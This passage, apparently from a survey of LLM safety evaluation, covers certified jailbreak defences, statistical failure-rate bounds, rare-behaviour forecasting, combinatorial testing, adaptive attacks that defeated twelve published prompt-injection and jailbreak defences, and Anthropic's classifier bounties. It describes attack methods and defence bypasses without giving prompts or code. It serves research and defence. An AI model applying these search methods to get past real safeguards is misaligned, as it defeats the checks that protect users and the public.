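Chen and colleagues certify a safety detector against an attacker who can replace tokens anywhere in a request, which erase-and-check does not cover. One version of their method makes copies of the request, blanks out each token with 10% probability, uses another model to fill in the gaps, and runs the detector on the results. If an attacker has changed two tokens, both are blanked out in 1% of the copies (0.1 × 0.1), and no trace of the change remains in those copies.

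Suppose the detector flags 99.5% of the copies of the original request. Even if all its misses fall within the 1% of copies where the change would be blanked out, it still flags half of that 1%. These copies are identical for the altered request, so the detector must flag at least 0.5% of the altered request's copies. If three tokens are changed, all three are blank in only 0.1% of copies. The detector could miss all of these, so the guarantee no longer holds.

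A guarantee of 0.5% is useful only if the detector blocks a prompt on very little evidence. Chen and colleagues set the threshold at 0.0046%, or about one flagged copy in 22,000. This is closer to Kumar and colleagues' rule, which blocks a prompt if even one version is flagged, than to a majority vote. When Chen and colleagues recalculated some of their results with a threshold of 10%, the certified number of changes fell to zero.

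With GPT-4o as the detector, the certificates covered an average of 2.02 changed tokens on 50 requests from AdvBench. Changing two or three tokens is often enough to make a harmful request harmless, for example by turning "hack into" into "log into". Chen and colleagues read the requests themselves and estimated that even a perfect detector could keep the same verdict for an average of only 2.12 changes. For a 16-token request and a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, two changes allow about 120 billion variants, while erase-and-check covers 10^90 suffixes.

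Certification takes a lot of computation. Chen and colleagues used a million altered copies to certify each request, and the full set of experiments took about two weeks on eight high-end processors. Each certificate holds with 99% confidence but does not cover inserted or deleted tokens. Their work also does not establish a false-alarm rate for new prompts, because they chose the threshold on the same harmless prompts that they used to check for false alarms.

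Their experiments also illustrate why a certificate is useful. Their strongest automated attack, with 20-token suffixes, left the smoothing defences more than 60% robust. But they could write a short suffix by hand that made their detector label a harmful request safe, so the randomness had made the search for such suffixes harder without removing the weakness.

### Newer guarantees and other attackers

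Recent methods try to make smoothing less damaging to ordinary use. *Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment* (Cheng, Yang and colleagues, 2026) describes a method that keeps the structural part of a prompt fixed, deletes random tokens from the rest, and trains the model to handle the gaps. The certificate covers a limited number of changed tokens and depends on how often the random deletions remove all of them. If an attacker changes five tokens in a 100-token prompt and the method keeps ten tokens at random, the deletions remove all five changed tokens about 58% of the time.

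On Llama 3, the defence reduced the success rate of automated suffix attacks from 84.2% to 1.2%. The model kept 94.1% of its usefulness on harmless prompts, compared with 74.3% under character-level smoothing. The 1.2% was measured against particular attacks, whereas the certificate holds for every attack within its limit. *Guaranteed Jailbreaking Defense via Disrupt-and-Rectify Smoothing* (2026) describes a defence that also alters prompts and repairs them, and bounds the probability that it succeeds.

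*Towards Poisoning Robustness Certification for Natural Language Generation* (2026) addresses an attacker who plants harmful examples in a model's training data instead of changing the prompt. It offers guarantees for how a model follows instructions and for which tools an agent calls. These guarantees do not limit what a hostile prompt can do to a model trained on clean data.

Erase-and-check is only as good as its filter, so a proof about the filter itself would be valuable. *Beyond Red-Teaming* (2026) attempts this for classifiers that detect toxic text. Such a classifier turns a text into a list of numbers, then calculates a score from their weighted sum. The researchers draw a box around the numbers that represent a kind of harmful text, with a lower and an upper limit for each number. The lowest score in the box is easy to find by setting each number with a positive weight to its lower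 limit and each number with a negative weight to its upper limit. If even this score is above the threshold for blocking, the classifier blocks everything in the box.

This proof covers only the last step of the calculation, unlike the proofs for models that pick the largest of four numbers, so it works even for a classifier built on Llama 3.1 8B. The researchers tested three classifiers, and every box they tried contained points that the classifier would let through. These points aren't necessarily jailbreaks, because there may be no text that produces those exact numbers.

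## Forecasting rare failures from a sample of prompts

A certificate covers only prompts of a certain form. Random sampling works for any kind of prompt, including the ordinary ones that make up most of a system's traffic, but it can only estimate how often the system fails.

### What a clean test shows

Suppose a tester picks n prompts at random from those that users send, runs each one, and finds no failures. If the system fails on a share p of such prompts, the chance of finding no failures is (1 − p)^n. For p = 0.1% and n = 3,000, this is just under 5%. The tester can therefore say with 95% confidence that the failure rate is below 0.1%. For other test sizes, this upper limit is about 3/n, because (1 − p)^n falls to 5% when n × p reaches about 3.

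But at a billion prompts a day, a failure rate just below 0.1% means almost a million failures a day. Lowering the limit to one failure a day would take three billion tests without a failure, or 35 days at 1,000 prompts a second. A single failure during those tests would raise the limit to about 4.7/n, and the tester would need over 50% more tests to bring it back down to one failure a day.

The bound also assumes that the test oracle recognises every failure. *ASTRAL* (Ugarte, Valle and colleagues, 2025) tested eight language models as judges of 353 unsafe and 353 safe answers. GPT-3.5 was the most accurate and recognised 90% of the unsafe answers. An early version of Llama Guard, which Meta built for this job, recognised only 36%. If a judge misses failures at these rates, a test of n prompts that finds no failures limits the failure rate to about 3.3/n with GPT-3.5 and 8.3/n with Llama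 Guard.

### Why testing cannot establish very low failure rates

*The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* (Butler and Finelli, 1993) applies the same formula to software that controls aircraft or nuclear reactors. The limit on the probability of failure for such systems is typically between 10^-7 and 10^-9 for a mission of one to ten hours. A system with a one-in-a-billion chance of failing in ten hours will run for an average of 10 billion hours, or 1.14 million years, before it fails. Running 10,000 copies at once would shorten the average wait to 114 years.

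Predicting reliability from how the failure rate falls as engineers repair bugs can still require an impractical amount of testing. Butler and Finelli tried this method on data from an earlier experiment with six programs. In one program, 98% of inputs failed after the first repair and 0.08% after the sixth. They fitted a straight line to the logarithms of the failure rates and extended it to predict that the program would meet the requirement after 23 repairs. But the 23rd bug would be so rare that finding it would take about 340,000 years.

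The argument is weaker for a system that receives inputs rarely but that testers can run quickly. If a system handles one input a month and a test takes a tenth of a second, the expected test time falls to 16 days. But a popular chatbot that receives a billion prompts a day handles about 11,600 a second, so a test at 1,000 prompts a second gathers evidence more slowly than ordinary use does.

Littlewood also concludes, in *The Problems of Assessing Software Reliability*, that the reliability anyone can claim for software on scientific grounds is "relatively modest". A modest claim is often enough for a chatbot. A company might accept one rude answer in 10,000, and 30,000 tests with no rude answers would support a claim that the rate is no higher than that. It would not accept the same rate for answers that help somebody make a weapon.

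### How close a prompt came to failing

A single pass-or-fail test shows little about how likely a prompt is to produce a harmful answer. A prompt that produces one in 50 attempts will usually pass, and so will a prompt that produces one in a trillion. In *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors*, Jones, Tong and colleagues (2025), most of whom worked at Anthropic, measured such differences in probability and used them to predict failures that had not yet occurred.

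The elicitation probability of a prompt is the chance that a randomly sampled answer to it shows a particular behaviour. Testers can measure it by sampling many answers and counting how many show the behaviour, but this is slow when the behaviour is rare. For one exact answer, they can calculate the probability without sampling, by multiplying the probabilities that the model gives to each of its tokens. If an answer has ten tokens and the model gives each a probability of 10%, the answer has a probability of one in 10 billion, which a tester can calculate in one run but could hardly measure by counting.

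The shortcut misses harmful answers that are worded differently, so Jones and colleagues also measured the probability of a single revealing keyword within the answer. In a smaller experiment, they sampled whole answers and checked whether the keyword appeared anywhere.

Three quantities describe the risk when a model receives n prompts:

- The worst-query risk is the highest elicitation probability among the n prompts.
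- The behaviour frequency is the share of prompts whose elicitation probability exceeds some threshold, such as 50%.
- The aggregate risk is the chance that at least one of the n prompts produces the behaviour when the model answers each prompt once.

The total risk can be high even when each prompt looks safe. If 100,000 prompts each have a one in 100,000 chance of producing a harmful answer, the chance of at least one harmful answer is 63%.

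### Extending the tail

To forecast these quantities for a large deployment, Jones and colleagues needed to know how the highest elicitation probability grows with the number of prompts. They used extreme value theory, the branch of statistics that deals with the largest values in a sample. Just as the average of many random values tends to follow a bell curve whatever the values look like, the largest value in a big sample tends, under fairly general conditions, to follow one of three types of distribution. Jones and colleagues assumed the Gumbel type.

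They first turn each elicitation probability p into a score, ψ = −log(−log p), which rises as p rises. If the Gumbel assumption holds, the share of prompts that score above ψ shrinks by the same factor for every equal step up in ψ. Written as a formula, for high scores,

log S(ψ) = aψ + b,

where S(ψ) is that share and a is a negative number. The forecast takes three steps:

1. Measure the elicitation probability of each of m test prompts and convert it to a score.
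2. Take the ten highest scores and fit a straight line through them, which gives a and b.
3. For a deployment of n prompts, find the score that one prompt in n should exceed, which is ψ = −(log n + b)/a, and convert it back to a probability.

In terms of the original probabilities, each tenfold increase in the number of prompts divides the exponent of the highest probability by a constant. Suppose the highest elicitation probability is 10^-8 among 100 prompts and 10^-4 among 1,000. The exponent has halved, so the forecast halves it again for each further tenfold increase, giving 10^-2 for 10,000 prompts, 10^-1 for 100,000 and about 0.3 for a million. The worst of the 1,000 test prompts would produce a harmful answer about once in 10,000 attempts, but the forecast is that a million prompts from users would include one that produces a harmful answer about 30% of the time.

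The Gumbel assumption rests partly on an analogy with training. Researchers had found that a model's error falls in a regular way as training continues, and Jones and colleagues suggest that drawing more prompts and keeping the worst resembles more training. If the true tail were heavier than the straight line, the forecast would be too low. In the experiment that sampled whole answers, many but not all of the tails followed the line for large samples.

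### How accurate the forecasts were

For the main experiment, Jones and colleagues chose 19 dangerous chemical and biological substances. They had a version of Claude 3.5 Sonnet without the usual refusals write 100,000 prompts for each one, intended to draw out harmful information. They then used tests on 100 to 1,000 prompts to forecast how Claude models would behave on up to 90,000, and compared the forecasts with the models' actual behaviour. For aggregate risk, they simulated deployments of up to 500,000 prompts by drawing repeatedly from the same pool.

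The baseline method fits a bell curve to the scores of all the test prompts instead of a line to the top ten. The errors below are averaged on a logarithmic scale and converted to factors, so a factor of 20 means a typical forecast was 20 times too high or too low.

| Quantity forecast | Typical error, line through the top ten | Typical error, bell curve |
|---|---|---|
| Worst-query risk | 50 | 250 |
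| Behaviour frequency | 6 to 7 | 2,000 to 11,000 |
| Aggregate risk, from 1,000 test prompts | 20 | 320 |

A few large misses raise the average error to a factor of 50. The forecast of worst-query risk was within a factor of ten 72% of the time, and 86% of the time when Jones and colleagues predicted the result for 90,000 prompts from 900. A forecast that is too low gives developers false confidence. The forecast was too low in 34% of cases, compared with 72% for the bell curve.

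When they sampled whole answers from Claude 3.5 Haiku, their forecasts of the worst-query risk were typically off by a factor of only 1.5. They limited this test to substances for which no prompt in a sample of 100 had an elicitation probability of 50% or more. In 75% of cases, the forecasts correctly predicted whether a larger set would contain such a prompt.

A second experiment dealt with ordinary use. Jones and colleagues generated 100,000 sets of operator instructions, which gave the model various personalities and jobs in fields such as sales or medicine. The model then answered two-option questions in which one option was to seek power, avoid being shut down, or copy itself elsewhere. Forecasts of the highest probability of choosing the bad option were off by an average of five percentage points, compared with 12 for the bell curve. When no test prompt had made the model prefer the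 bad option, the errors were 14 and 18 points, respectively. The questions were artificial, and a model that picks an option on a questionnaire might not take the same action in a real task.

The forecasts can also help a red team decide how to spend its budget. In 223 settings, Jones and colleagues predicted whether a cheap model writing many attack prompts or an expensive one writing few would find the more effective prompt. They were right 63% of the time, compared with 54% for always giving the more common answer. Their accuracy was 79% when the two results differed by a factor of more than 100.

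Because the line depends on ten prompts, another random test set can give a noticeably different forecast. Jones and colleagues expect the method to extend to billions of prompts with only slightly more extrapolation, but they tested it only on deployments up to 1,000 times the size of the test set. Forecasting from 1,000 prompts to a billion would mean extrapolating by a factor of a million. In their red-team experiment, the forecasts were somewhat too high, and the error grew as they extrapolated further.

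### Estimating one output in a billion

Wu and Hilton (2024), in *Estimating the Probabilities of Rare Outputs in Language Models*, studied a simpler problem in which they could check the answers more precisely. They fed random sequences, such as strings of hexadecimal characters or unconnected English words, to transformers with one, two or four layers, and tried to estimate how often a chosen token would be the model's top prediction for the next token. They measured the actual rates by running each model on 2^32 (4.3 billion) inputs, then selected tokens with rates between 10^-9 and 10^-5. A token with a rate of 10^-9 would be the top prediction only about four times in 4.3 billion inputs, so even the measured rates are approximate.

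Wu and Hilton compared two approaches. Each estimation method could use only 2^16 (65,536) runs, too few for most of these events to appear even once in ordinary sampling.

The first, importance sampling, draws inputs from an altered distribution in which the rare output is more common, then corrects for the alteration. Suppose an input that triggers the output has a probability of one in a billion under the original distribution and one in 1,000 under the altered one. The tester counts each appearance of that input as a millionth of a case. The average over many draws is then an unbiased estimate of the output's original rate. One of their methods uses a search adapted from Zou and colleagues' search for attack suffixes to find inputs likely to trigger the output.

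The second approach can estimate how likely a token is without finding an input that produces it. It records the model's internal state just before the final step for each of the 65,536 runs and splits each state into two parts, one of which lies in a direction that favours the chosen token. Combining every first part with every second part gives 4.3 billion artificial states, and the estimate is the share of them that would lead to the token. This estimate is reliable only if the two parts are independent, but the method guarantees just the weaker condition that they are uncorrelated.

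Both approaches beat ordinary sampling, and importance sampling was generally more accurate. Wu and Hilton remain interested in the second approach because importance sampling depends on finding inputs that trigger the behaviour. If the search finds none, the estimate is zero, which is as misleading as a test that finds no failures.

Wu and Hilton's scoring formula did not work for estimates of exactly zero, so they adjusted each method's results using the true rates, which a developer with a real system would not know. Parulekar and Liu (2026) point out this problem in *Estimating Rare Events in Language Models with Proper Evaluation* and propose a score that accepts zeros and lets the user decide how much worse an underestimate is than an overestimate.

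They also propose a new method, which reaches a rare event through a chain of less rare ones. For example, a one-in-a-million event could be split into six stages, each of which one case in ten survives. At each stage, the method discards the internal states furthest from producing the chosen token, copies the rest, and changes the copies slightly while keeping them close to what the model normally produces. When overestimates and underestimates counted about equally, the new method beat Wu and Hilton's artificial states for the one-layer and four-layer models and nearly tied for the two-layer model. When underestimates counted much more, the older method could do better because it tends to overestimate. A developer may prefer a method that overestimates the probability of a catastrophic failure to one that underestimates it.

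All these experiments used random text, models with at most four layers, and a single token as the outcome. Whether an answer counts as harmful depends on many tokens together and on a judge that can make mistakes, so the methods are still far from being able to estimate the rate of harmful answers in a commercial model.

### Prompts from outside the sample

Every estimate of this kind holds only for the distribution of prompts that the tester sampled from. Suppose one prompt in 100,000 is an attack, every attack succeeds, and the system never fails otherwise. The overall failure rate is 0.001%, and a random sample of 3,000 prompts has a 97% chance of containing no attacks. The tester would then correctly report a failure rate below 0.1%, even though the system fails on every attack.

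The tester can sample attack prompts separately, as Jones and colleagues did, but the result applies only to attacks like those in the collection. Jones and colleagues studied attackers who do not adapt, and they warn that real ones may adjust their prompts to the model. An attacker who searches for failures can find a one-in-a-billion prompt and send it every day. Ordinary users can also change the mix of prompts, for instance when they start using a model for a new kind of work. Jones and colleagues suggest sampling from past use and updating the forecast as new prompts arrive, which would help with gradual changes.

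An attacker can also repeat the same request. In *Jailbreak Scaling Laws for Large Language Models*, Halder, Banerjee and Pehlevan (2026) studied how the chance of at least one harmful answer grows with the number of attempts. The growth depends on the requests that the model is most likely to answer safely. Suppose that the model's chance of answering safely is spread evenly between 0% and 100% across a set of harmful requests. After nine attempts at each request, one in ten has still not produced a harmful answer. After 99 attempts it is one in 100, and after 999 it is one in 1,000. This share shrinks slowly because the model answers some requests safely almost every time.

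If the attacker adds text that lowers the top of the range from 100% to 90%, only about one request in 3.4 million would still be refused after 99 attempts. Halder and colleagues found the slow, polynomial pattern in models without such added text. Under attack, weaker models such as Llama 3.2 3B followed a faster pattern with an exponential part, while a stronger OpenAI model still followed the slow one.

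*Escaping Alignment* (2026) attributes this kind of exponential pattern to small test sets. Once every request in a set except the hardest has produced a harmful answer, the rest of the curve depends on one request with a fixed chance of failure on each attempt, and such a curve is always exponential. The paper tried up to 10,000 random variations of each request, and the curve became exponential at around 1,000 attempts. Halder and colleagues used attack text produced by a computer search, so the explanation may not fit their results. In either case, an attack success rate means little without the number of attempts.

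### Covering every pair of features

Random samples of prompts contain few unusual combinations of features, such as a misspelled medical question in Welsh. Combinatorial testing includes them on purpose. The tester lists the features that might matter, picks a few values for each, and chooses tests so that every combination of a small number of values occurs at least once.

Suppose the features are language (English or French), tone (polite or rude) and length (short or long). There are eight combinations, but four tests cover every pair of values:

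| Test | Language | Tone | Length |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | English | Polite | Short |
| 2 | English | Rude | Long |
| 3 | French | Polite | Long |
| 4 | French | Rude | Short |

A table like this is called a covering array, and it saves many more tests as the number of features grows. Ten features with five values each have 5^10 = 9,765,625 combinations, but only 1,125 pairs of values. Each test covers 45 pairs, so a few dozen tests can cover them all. At 1,000 prompts a second, running every combination once would take under three hours, but running each one 300 times to catch rare answers would take 34 days. With 20 features, running every combination once would take about 3,000 years, while a few dozen tests would still cover all the pairs.

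Testing combinations of input values works well for ordinary software because bugs usually depend on only a few conditions at once. According to NIST, researchers have never seen a software failure that involved more than six factors, so tests that cover every combination of five or six values are "pseudo exhaustive". IEEE's *Combinatorial Testing* describes combinations of two or three as sufficient for most systems. No comparable evidence exists for language models, which do not make decisions through explicit conditions on a few variables.

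Garn et al. (2023) made an early attempt to use the method on language models in *Applying Pairwise Combinatorial Testing to Large Language Model Testing*. They treated each word of a sentence as a feature and its synonyms as the values, then checked whether the model responded consistently. *Imperative Interference* (2026) used pairwise tests to measure how 22 blocks of instructions in one operator's prompt affect each other. Switching each block on or off gives about 4.2 million combinations.

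In *Evaluating Large Language Model Robustness using Combinatorial Testing*, Chandrasekaran, Patel and colleagues (2025) changed the order of the options in multiple-choice questions. Four options have 24 possible orders, but six are enough to show any three options in every relative order. GPT-3.5 Turbo answered 88% of the marketing questions correctly, yet for 21% of them at least one of the six reorderings changed its answer. Across four subjects, testing the six orders found between 78% and 100% of the questions whose answers changed under any of the 23 alternative orders. Chandrasekaran and colleagues did not test six random orders, which might have done nearly as well. They also found that the model sometimes gave different answers to the same order. Covering arrays, such as this set of six orders, normally include each combination just once, which is too few for a system with random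 answers.

Ugarte and colleagues applied the idea to safety with ASTRAL, a tool that has a language model write prompts for each combination of 14 harmful topics, six writing styles and five ways of persuading the tested model. ASTRAL can reduce the 420 combinations to a pairwise set, but the evaluation used all of them, with three prompts each. On most of the seven models tested, these prompts exposed about twice as many unsafe answers as the same number of prompts from an existing collection. On Llama 3 and Vicuna, the best version of ASTRAL exposed only 22% and 31% more. The language model writing the prompts also saw examples of successful prompts, and in one version it searched recent news, so the comparison does not show how much of the gain came from covering the combinations.

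### When the features are badly chosen

Wan and Wang (2026), in *M3-Test*, measured what pairwise tests miss. They gave four models 1,500 questions about photographs and altered both the photograph and the question. Each could be altered in five ways, such as blur for the photograph or typing errors for the question, at four strengths. That makes 20 alterations of each, and 400 combinations. They ran all 400 for every question, so they knew every failure in the set.

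Two Qwen models passed every test with a single alteration on some questions, but failed on at least one combination of alterations for 26% to 29% of those questions. These failures were easy to miss because fewer than 0.6% of the combinations failed. A pairwise array of 25 tests found 53% to 57% of the affected questions. Starting with the strongest alterations found 65% to 68% with the same number of tests, and ordering the tests by where other models had failed found about 80%.

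The number of tests needed to cover every pair depends on how the tester divides the prompt into features. Wan and Wang's array covered every pair in 25 tests only because they described each test by four features, the kind and strength of the alteration to the photograph and the kind and strength of the alteration to the question. A pairwise array can leave out a photograph blurred at strength two with typing errors at strength three, because that combination involves all four features. If Wan and Wang had treated each altered photograph and each altered question as a single value, they would have had two features with 20 values each, and covering every pair would have taken all 400 tests.

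Each combination of features also stands for a huge number of prompts. A model may refuse one prompt and answer another with the same features, so trying three of them samples that combination very thinly. The 3/n bound does not apply to the whole set of tests, because they are not a random sample of what users send. If the tester never lists language as a feature, a complete array may contain only English prompts and miss every failure that appears only in other languages.

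## Attacking twelve published defences with adaptive search

A random sample of prompts shows how a system behaves when nobody is trying to break it. An attacker needs only one prompt that works, and can search for it by trying a prompt, studying the response and revising the prompt. An adaptive attack is designed or adjusted to beat the particular defence under test. In 2025, researchers used adaptive attacks to break twelve published defences, most of which had stopped nearly every attack in their developers' own tests.

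### Why an attacker need not try everything

If one prompt in a trillion (10^12) gets past a model's safety rules, the model would almost certainly pass any random test of practical size. But with a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, there are about 10^90 ways to add 20 tokens to a request, and at that rate about 10^78 of them would work. Finding one by random guessing would take a trillion attempts on average, or about 32 years at 1,000 prompts a second.

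Feedback makes the search much faster. A lock with 20 dials, each with 32,000 positions, has as many combinations as there are suffixes. A thief who learns only whether the lock has opened must guess whole combinations. If each dial clicks at the right position, the thief can set the dials one at a time and would need at most 640,000 tries, or 11 minutes at the same speed.

A language model's signals are less exact, because the effect of one token depends on the others, but they still show progress. A change to a prompt might raise the chance of a harmful answer from one in a billion to one in a million. The attacker may still see only refusals, but an attacker who can read the model's probabilities knows to keep that change. Zou and colleagues automated this kind of search for suffixes in *Universal and Transferable Adversarial Attacks on Aligned Language Models* (2023). Nasr, Carlini and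 colleagues report in *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) that this method uses 500 rounds of 512 queries, or 256,000 in all, to find 20 tokens. Researchers have to measure how long a search takes, because the impossibility proofs give no estimate.

### Four kinds of search

Nasr and colleagues, including Schulhoff, worked at OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other organisations. In all their attacks, the attacker repeatedly proposes some prompts, scores the results and uses the most promising prompts to write the next batch.

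The twelve defences faced four kinds of attack. Gradient methods use a model's internal numbers to calculate which token changes are likely to help the attack. Reinforcement learning trains a second model to write attacks by rewarding it when they work. Evolutionary search keeps a pool of promising attacks and asks a language model for variations on them. In the fourth kind, people wrote the attacks themselves.

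In an adaptive search, scoring the attempts well matters as much as proposing them. Nasr and colleagues had another model grade each attempt from 1 to 10 because, they note, a plain yes or no would have turned their evolutionary search into random guessing. In the reinforcement learning attack on one defence, the attacker failed almost completely until, partway through training, it found a few prompts that partly worked. It then improved quickly.

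Automatic scoring also produced false successes. One attacker found that repeating a phrase many times earned a high score, although this showed nothing about the defence. Nasr and colleagues therefore checked the successful attacks by hand.

### What happened to the defences

Nasr and colleagues tested most of the prompt injection defences on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an agent does office tasks with tools such as email while reading text that an attacker may have planted. The benchmark's own attack uses the same template for every case. On 80 cases, they compared this attack with their evolutionary search, which was allowed up to 800 attempts per case. The table gives the results for agents running on Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. The median number of attempts counts only the cases where the search succeeded.

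| Defence | Method | Ordinary tasks completed | Fixed attack succeeds | Adaptive search succeeds | Median attempts to first success |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 74% | 30% | 100% | 13 |
| Spotlighting | Marks the text that the model should trust | 75% | 28% | 99% | 14 |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | 73% | 21% | 95% | 14 |
| PromptGuard | Filter | 72% | 26% | 94% | 21 |
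| Model Armor | Filter | 59% | 28% | 90% | 22 |
| Protect AI | Filter | 39% | 15% | 90% | 30 |
| MELON | Runs the agent twice and compares its actions | 58% | 0% | 89% | 20 |
| PIGuard | Filter | 39% | 0% | 71% | 46 |

MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a harmless one. If the agent still takes the same actions, the text it read must have caused them. On Meta's Llama 3.3 70B, the search got past MELON in 76% of cases without any information about how the defence worked, and in 95% when given a description of it.

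MetaSecAlign, a version of Llama trained to resist prompt injection, had a reported attack success rate of 2% on AgentDojo. Adaptive search raised it to 96%.

Nasr and colleagues tested the other four defences on different benchmarks:

- RPO adds a specially optimised safety instruction to each prompt to prevent jailbreaks. Gradient search succeeded 96% of the time and reinforcement learning 98%.
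- Circuit Breakers trains a model on attack prompts to make it resist jailbreaks. Reinforcement learning succeeded every time.
- StruQ trains a model to ignore instructions in the data it reads. Reinforcement learning succeeded in every case here too, although the attacker's goal was only to make the model print a chosen phrase.
- Data Sentinel asks a model to repeat a secret word while it ignores the incoming text, and blocks the text if the model fails. Its developers reported that it missed almost no attacks. Nasr and colleagues got past it in every case and made the model do the attacker's task with over 80% accuracy, about as well as with no defence.

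These percentages cannot be used to rank the defences, because the benchmarks and attackers differed. Nasr and colleagues also gave the attacker generous conditions, such as access to the filters' confidence scores, which a commercial product might hide. They justify this with the usual assumption in security research that the attacker knows the design and has plenty of computing power. In practice, the attacks needed little computing power. Against Gemini, the typical successful search took fewer than 50 attempts, whatever the defence.

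Some defences made attacks harder. The search succeeded against GPT-5 Mini, a small OpenAI model, in 75% of cases without a defence, 49% with PIGuard and 47% with Spotlighting. Spotlighting is based on prompting, so its result does not fit Nasr and colleagues' conclusion that such defences add no robustness. They expect that a larger search would also defeat GPT-5 Mini most of the time, but did not run one.

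### Why a fixed list of attacks overstates a defence

The fixed attack never succeeded against GPT-5 Mini, with or without a defence. A developer who relied on that test would have reported a zero attack success rate for any defence, even one that did nothing. The adaptive search succeeded in 47% to 81% of cases, depending on the defence.

A list of known jailbreaks goes out of date because companies train newer models to refuse many of the prompts on it. Some developers also use such lists to build their defences, so testing those defences on similar prompts doesn't show how well they would block new kinds of attack.

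Nasr and colleagues compare these results with earlier research on image classifiers, where training on a fixed set of manipulated images failed to protect against new ones. Training gave useful protection only when developers searched for new attacks during training, and only against the kinds of attack they searched for. Nasr and colleagues also conclude that an experiment can never prove a defence robust and can only show that a serious attempt failed to break it, which is close to Dijkstra's point about bugs.

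### People against the search

More than 500 people took part in a contest that Nasr and colleagues ran alongside their automated attacks. The contest had 40 challenges, $20,000 in prizes and a bonus for the shortest successful attack. Contestants did not know which challenges had a defence, and together they beat all 40.

Human contestants and the search both attempted 29 combinations of model and defence. The contestants as a group succeeded on all 29, and the search succeeded on 69%. This comparison favours the people, since up to several hundred of them worked on each challenge and the search ran only once. Three people tried all 29 combinations. The best of them solved 75%, and the search did better than the other two.

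The success rate per attempt is weak evidence of whether a defence holds, because anyone can reuse a prompt that has succeeded once. MELON reduced the rate from 11.1% to 0.4% on one version of Gemini 2.5 Pro, so an average contestant would have needed about 250 attempts instead of nine, but somebody still succeeded. Other defences seemed to raise the success rate. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, attacks succeeded 28.8% of the time without Spotlighting and 43.7% with it. Each comparison used a single task, and contestants varied greatly in skill, so differences of this size may not come from the defence.

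### Anthropic's classifiers and thousands of hours of attacks

The twelve defences were mostly research prototypes or small filters. A company that spends more on a narrower goal can make attacks much harder. Sharma, Tong and colleagues (2025), in *Constitutional Classifiers*, describe guardrails that Anthropic built to stop its Claude models from helping with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. The developers write a list of permitted and forbidden kinds of content, called a constitution. A language model generates examples from this list, and the developers use them to train one classifier for prompts and another for answers.

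The goal was to prevent universal jailbreaks, which are single methods that work on nearly all the harmful questions in a field. Someone trying to make a weapon needs reliable answers to many questions, so one lucky answer is much less dangerous.

Anthropic offered up to $15,000 for a method that would get detailed answers to ten forbidden questions. It invited 405 people, of whom 183 were active. Sharma and colleagues estimate that the participants spent 4,720 hours on the task (90% confidence interval 3,242 to 7,417). None of the 113 reports they submitted answered all ten questions with at least half the detail of an unprotected model. Nine answered more than six questions at that standard. Anthropic paid out a total of $95,000.

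This prototype refused about 44% of ordinary traffic, so it was unusable as a product. A later version raised refusals by only 0.38 percentage points and required 23.7% more computation. In an automated test on 10,000 jailbreak prompts, the later version reduced the jailbreak success rate from 86% to 4.4%. The public challenge that followed was a more demanding test, because the automated one used a fixed list of prompts and so had the weakness just described.

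Anthropic's *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025) reports a public test, held over a week in February 2025, in which anyone could try to get a model to answer eight questions about chemical weapons. The 339 people who got past at least one question spent about 3,700 hours on the challenge. Nobody got answers to all eight in the first five days. Four people did in the last two days, and Anthropic judged that one of them had found a universal jailbreak.

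The conditions helped the attackers. They learned at once from an automatic grader whether an answer was detailed enough, whereas a real criminal would have to try the instructions out. Anthropic also left the classifiers unchanged all week, although a company can normally respond when it sees an attack.

### Newer versions

*Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) tests four later systems with similar bounties and compares them. It counts a failure as serious if one attack method gets answers to more than five of eight questions with at least half the detail an unprotected model gives.

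| System | Attempts | Serious failures | Failures per million attempts | Methods that answered all eight questions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate checks on prompt and answer | 695,000 | 13 | 18.7 | 4 |
| One check on prompt and answer together | 226,000 | 2 | 8.9 | 1 |
| Cheap check first, stronger check if needed | 569,000 | 5 | 8.8 | 0 |
| Production version | 198,000 | 1 | 5.1 | 0 |

The production version also used about a twenty-eighth of the computing power of the oldest system and refused 0.05% of ordinary traffic. But the evidence that it is harder to break is weak, because serious failures are rare. If it failed as often as the oldest system, 198,000 attempts would produce 3.7 serious failures on average, with about a 12% chance of seeing one or none. Cunningham and colleagues also changed the questions and the rewards between tests.

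A bounty's result depends on who takes part. No one in the bounty programme found a universal jailbreak for the third system in the table, but outside experts did, using automated tools and substantial effort. In February 2026, the British government's AI Security Institute (UK AISI) announced an automated technique that produces universal jailbreaks against the best-defended systems.

Getting past a defence can also make the model's answers less accurate. Cunningham and colleagues tested two methods of evading the classifiers on a set of hard science questions. Claude Opus 4 normally answered 74.2% of them correctly, but only 32.3% with one method and 49% with the other. The gap between the two suggests that another method might preserve even more of the model's ability.

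### Effort to break as a measure

If skilled testers eventually break every system, the time they need is more informative than whether they succeed. The UK AISI red team led by Xander Davies had jailbroken every model it tested. His *State of Jailbreaks* compares two models released six months apart. The team broke the earlier one in about ten minutes with a public attack, but needed more than seven hours to break the later one. UK AISI's *Frontier AI Trends Report* also gives a 40-fold difference in expert effort between two models released six months apart.

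Davies attributes such gains mainly to companies' deliberate work on safeguards, and more capable models are only slightly more robust. The protection was narrow. On one model, it took around five hours to get help with biological weapons but about ten minutes to get help with other harmful requests. An average across all categories would have hidden this difference.

By May 2026, the same team had broken the safeguards on OpenAI's newest ChatGPT and got hacking tips from it in about six hours, according to The Star's *Inside the British lab hunting for dangers lurking in AI* (2026).

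Hours are a rough unit, as Davies acknowledges, because they depend on the testers' skill and tools. They also depend on whose time is counted. The one serious failure in Anthropic's production version took its discoverer 30 hours to find, while all the testers together spent 1,736 hours. The total is a better guide to how hard the system is to break, because it includes the time of testers who failed. But a company that faces thousands of attackers should expect some to be as lucky or skilled as that discoverer.

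The costs of attacks are easier to compare in money. In *AI Security Leaderboard*, Timm, Struppek and colleagues (2026), who work with the research organisation FAR.AI, estimated how much an attacker would spend to find one universal jailbreak by automated random search. In July 2026 they tested four companies' leading models. They collected 67 building blocks of known jailbreaks, which can form more than 100 million combinations, and tried 1,000 random combinations on each model. Experts then assembled another 500 combinations. A jailbreak counted as universal if it worked on more than 75% of the harmful requests in at least one of five fields, four involving weapons and one involving cyberattacks.

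| Model | Universal jailbreaks in 1,000 random combinations | Universal jailbreaks in 500 expert combinations | Estimated cost of finding one at random |
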